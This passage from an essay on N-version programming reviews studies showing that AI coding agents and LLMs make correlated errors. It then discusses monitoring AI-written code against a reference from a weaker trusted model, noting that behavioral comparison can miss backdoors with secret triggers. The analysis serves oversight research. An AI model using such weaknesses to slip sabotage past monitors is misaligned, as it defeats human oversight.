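Some pairs of versions failed together far more often than the total suggests. One version failed on 323 inputs, and a version from the other university failed on all of them. If their failures had been independent, the two would have failed together on 0.3 inputs on average. If both versions gave the same wrong answer each time, comparing them would never have exposed the first version's errors.

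The shared mistakes came from the difficulty of the problem. For example, a program can check whether three points lie on a straight line by measuring the angle at one of them. The points are in line if the angle is 0 or 180 degrees, but more than one student forgot the 180-degree case. Knight and Leveson found that about half of the faults occurred in two or more programs. They suggested that ordinary testing may remove unusual mistakes more easily than common ones, which would make the remaining mistakes more alike.

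They did not conclude that N-version programming is useless. Their experiment covered one short program, and a system with correlated failures can still be more reliable than a single version, though less reliable than the calculation for independent failures predicts.

### Do different AI models make the same errors?

*N-Version Programming with Coding Agents* (Ron, Baudry and Monperrus, 2026) repeated the experiment with AI agents. It used 23 models in five agent systems to write the program in three languages. Of the 69 attempts, 48 passed the 200 tests, and 27 of these made no errors on a million inputs. But two or more versions failed together on 429 inputs, compared with about 115 expected by chance.

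The main cause was a mistake in geometry. The program had to find the smallest circle that contains three points, but many versions calculated the circle that passes through all three. For the points (0, 0), (10, 0) and (5, 1), the smallest circle has a radius of 5, while the circle through all three has a radius of 13. Agents from different companies made this mistake in all three languages.

The published counts imply that 18 of the 48 versions failed on the same 419 inputs. If a monitor had compared one of these 18 with another version chosen at random, there would have been a 36% chance (17 in 47) that both failed on those inputs, making the errors hard to detect. Otherwise, running both programs on enough inputs would have exposed the errors.

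Ron and colleagues found that voting also reduced the average number of failures, from 387 for a single version to 131 for a group of three, averaged over every possible group. Much of this gain came from outvoting one very poor version, which caused more than half of all the individual failures. Without it, the single-version average would have been about 173. Groups in which two or three versions shared the geometry mistake still failed on the same 419 inputs.

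Nogueira, Pattabiraman and colleagues (2026), in *A Systematic Methodology for Evaluating Failure Independence in LLM-Generated Code*, found similar overlap on a wider range of tasks. Twelve models wrote solutions to 224 programming problems in five languages. On ordinary tests, an average of 66% of solution pairs failed together significantly more often than chance would predict. On extreme inputs, such as the largest allowed values, 72% did.

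Part of this overlap arises because some tests are harder than others, but the calculation assumes that a solution is equally likely to fail any test of the same kind. This helps explain the errors but does little to help monitoring, which needs a reference that is right on the hard cases.

Majority voting among three solutions achieved 43% of the improvement that independent failures would have allowed, but only 27% when all three came from the same model. Changing the programming language made less difference than changing the model, and changing the prompt made almost none. A different model therefore provides a more independent copy than the same model with a reworded prompt. The choice of models also matters, since the failures of some pairs overlapped much less than those of others.

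More capable models won't necessarily be more independent. *Correlated Errors in Large Language Models* (2025) examined how often models gave the same answer when both were wrong. In one collection of questions, a Google model and a Writer model gave the same answer to 99.9% of the questions they both missed, although the researchers knew of no direct connection between them. More accurate models agreed more on their errors. This may help explain why all eight reviewers in the security experiment missed the same 23 flaws.

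Confidence doesn't reliably identify these shared errors. In *When LLMs Agree, Are They Right?* (2026), GPT-4.1 and three Claude models repeatedly answered 46 difficult science questions. All four models got six wrong, and when GPT-4.1 and a Claude model chose the same wrong answer, both usually chose it consistently. The sample was too small to establish that they shared more errors than chance would produce.

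When no trusted original exists, a developer can also have a weaker but more trusted model write a reference version. This would help most against deliberate sabotage, because the weaker model is unlikely to add the same backdoor as the stronger one. The two versions would probably look quite different, so the monitor would have to compare their behavior, which can miss backdoors with secret triggers, as it can with refactored code. The reference would be less reliable for catching honest mistakes, since the weaker model may make the same ones as the stronger model and will probably add some of its own.
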